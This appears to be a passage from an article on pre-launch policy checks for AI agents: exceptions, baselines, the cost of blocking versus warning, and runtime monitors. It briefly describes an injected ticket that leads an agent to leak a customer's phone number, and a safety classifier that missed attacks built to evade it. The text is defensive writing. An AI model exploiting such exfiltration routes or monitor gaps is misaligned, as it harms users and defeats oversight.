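Some owners will have a good reason to launch anyway. Suppose the shop's head of support wants unrestricted parcel tracking until the Christmas rush is over. An exception could look like this, in an invented format:

```yaml
- agent: support
  rule: trifecta
  owner: head-of-support
  reason: Carrier list not ready before Christmas
  expires: 2027-01-15
  approved_settings: <fingerprint of tools, tokens and hosts>
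```

The owner answers for the risk and is the person the security team can ask about it later. The expiry date matters because people forget to remove exceptions that cause no trouble. According to *Filtering*, the Trivy scanner's documentation on ignoring findings, the reason and expiry date are both optional, and an exception without a date never expires. A company can make both fields compulsory with another policy. *Agentic process evidence* (2026) notes that an engine like OPA can easily check whether a record names an owner or includes a human review. Such an engine can't determine whether the reason is sound.

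Someone other than the developer should grant the exception. In a process that artis3n describes, the development team files a ticket with a short justification, the security team approves it, and the exception enters a shared repository as a pull request. *Policy Exceptions*, from the documentation for the Kubernetes policy engine Kyverno, adds optional compensating controls, which are conditions that must hold for the exception to apply. For example, the shop could require human approval of every web request until January.

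Exceptions should also be narrow. Conftest's *Exceptions* recommends naming rules so that an exception can target just one, because an exception with an empty name switches off every unnamed `deny` rule for the matching file. Conftest counts exceptions separately in its results, so a team can notice when the number grows.

A company that starts checking 200 existing agents may get dozens of findings on the first day. It can save these known findings in a list called a baseline, so that the check fails only on new ones. Checkov offers this for infrastructure code, and AgentShield's *Baselines* offers it for extensions to AI agents. AgentShield warns that a baseline "does not mark findings as safe" and advises against letting the build system rewrite it automatically, because that would hide new problems. Old agents are as exposed as new ones, so the company should treat the baseline as a to-do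 list with an owner for each finding.

A simple baseline can hide a combination finding that has become more serious. Suppose the baseline contains "support agent has the trifecta", and a colleague then gives the agent access to the payroll. The possible loss is now much greater, but the finding has the same name, so it stays hidden. The fingerprint in the shop's exception prevents this because it covers the tools, what their tokens can access and the allowed hosts, and any change to these cancels the exception and starts a new check. A remote server can add tools without anyone editing a file, so the check should run again whenever the agent starts, using the current list of tools.

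### Blocking or warning

A check can stop the launch or merely warn the developer. Suppose it produces 100 findings a year. These figures are invented:

- Stopping a launch costs $500 in staff time and delay, whether the finding is right or wrong, and every dangerous agent that the check stops gets repaired.
- After a warning, developers repair half of the dangerous agents, and the rest go live.
- Each dangerous agent that goes live has a 2% chance of a theft costing $100,000, which is an expected loss of $2,000.

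| Precision | Cost of blocking | Cost of warning |
|---|---|---|
| 80% | 100 × $500 = $50,000 | 80 × ½ × $2,000 = $80,000 |
| 30% | 100 × $500 = $50,000 | 30 × ½ × $2,000 = $30,000 |

Blocking is cheaper at 80% precision and warning is cheaper at 30%. They cost the same when precision is

500 / (½ × 2,000) = 50%

The possible loss affects the decision at least as much as precision does. Blocking pays off at any precision above 5% for an agent with access to the payroll and an expected loss of $20,000, but at no precision for an agent whose only private data is the lunch menu. The calculation overstates the benefit of blocking in one respect, because developers who are wrongly blocked a few times may start running their agents from laptops, where nothing checks them.

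A company can handle the same finding differently for different agents. Conftest has separate `deny` and `warn` rules, and by default only a `deny` produces a failing exit code. Checkov lets a company choose which checks or severity levels block deployment. A new rule can start as a warning while the team measures its precision, then begin to block the agents whose failure would do the most damage.

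### The case for runtime control

Kaptein and colleagues argue that nobody can fully govern an agent before it runs, because many violations arise from a sequence of steps that the model chooses while running. Reading a database and sending an e-mail are each harmless, but sending the e-mail after reading the database may leak data. Permissions fixed in advance don't account for what the agent has already done, so they must either allow both steps or forbid one of them. Only a program that tracks the steps so far can allow the harmless sequences and stop the harmful ones.

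They express this as a function that takes the agent's identity, its steps so far, the proposed next step and the state of the organisation, and returns the probability of a violation. A fixed permission is the special case that ignores the earlier steps.

The argument is right about precision, since a runtime monitor could let the shop's agent look up customers and track parcels, and stop only the web request that contained Dana Reyes's phone number. However, the paper presents no experiments, and Kaptein and Khan are affiliated with a company, Kyvvu. Vendors of runtime products take the same view. In *The Lethal Trifecta and How to Defend Against It*, Pearcy (2025) calls on companies to "go beyond static defenses" and recommends runtime monitoring, which the article's publisher, HiddenLayer, sells.

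Although AWS has its own provers, some of its guidance criticizes static checks. AWS's *AGENTSEC09-BP01 Integrate AI-powered vulnerability scanning across the development lifecycle* lists two common mistakes: relying on rule-based static analysis, which misses problems such as broken access control between agents, and scanning only at deployment, when repairs are expensive. It recommends having AI review the design documents, every pull request and the running application, preferably with AWS's own product. This supports checking before deployment as much as after it. The criticism of rules applies mainly to those that match one known pattern, and less to those that combine the labels of several agents.

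A check before launch can prevent a whole class of thefts without recognising any of them. If the agent has no route to the attacker, it doesn't matter how the ticket is worded or whether the stolen number is disguised. Kaptein and colleagues accept this, and call the removal of a permission "genuine enforcement". A runtime monitor, by contrast, has to make the right decision every time. Anthropic's classifier for Claude Code, one of the better-tested examples, blocked 89% of the dangerous commands that the paid testers saw. After improvements, it still missed 7% of the attacks that Apollo Research, an AI safety company, had built to defeat it. Anthropic says the classifier "does not eliminate risk".

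Developers also have more ways to fix a problem before launch. A monitor can allow a call, block it or ask someone, but a developer who gets the finding while building the agent can replace `http_get` with a parcel-tracking tool before any customer or colleague depends on the old one.

A monitor protects an agent only if it is connected, is switched on and receives every call. These are also configuration settings, so a policy can block the launch of an agent whose sandbox is allowed to fail silently, or whose gateway logs its decisions without enforcing them. The shop could permit the full trifecta only when such a monitor is in place, and use OPA to check this each time the agent starts.
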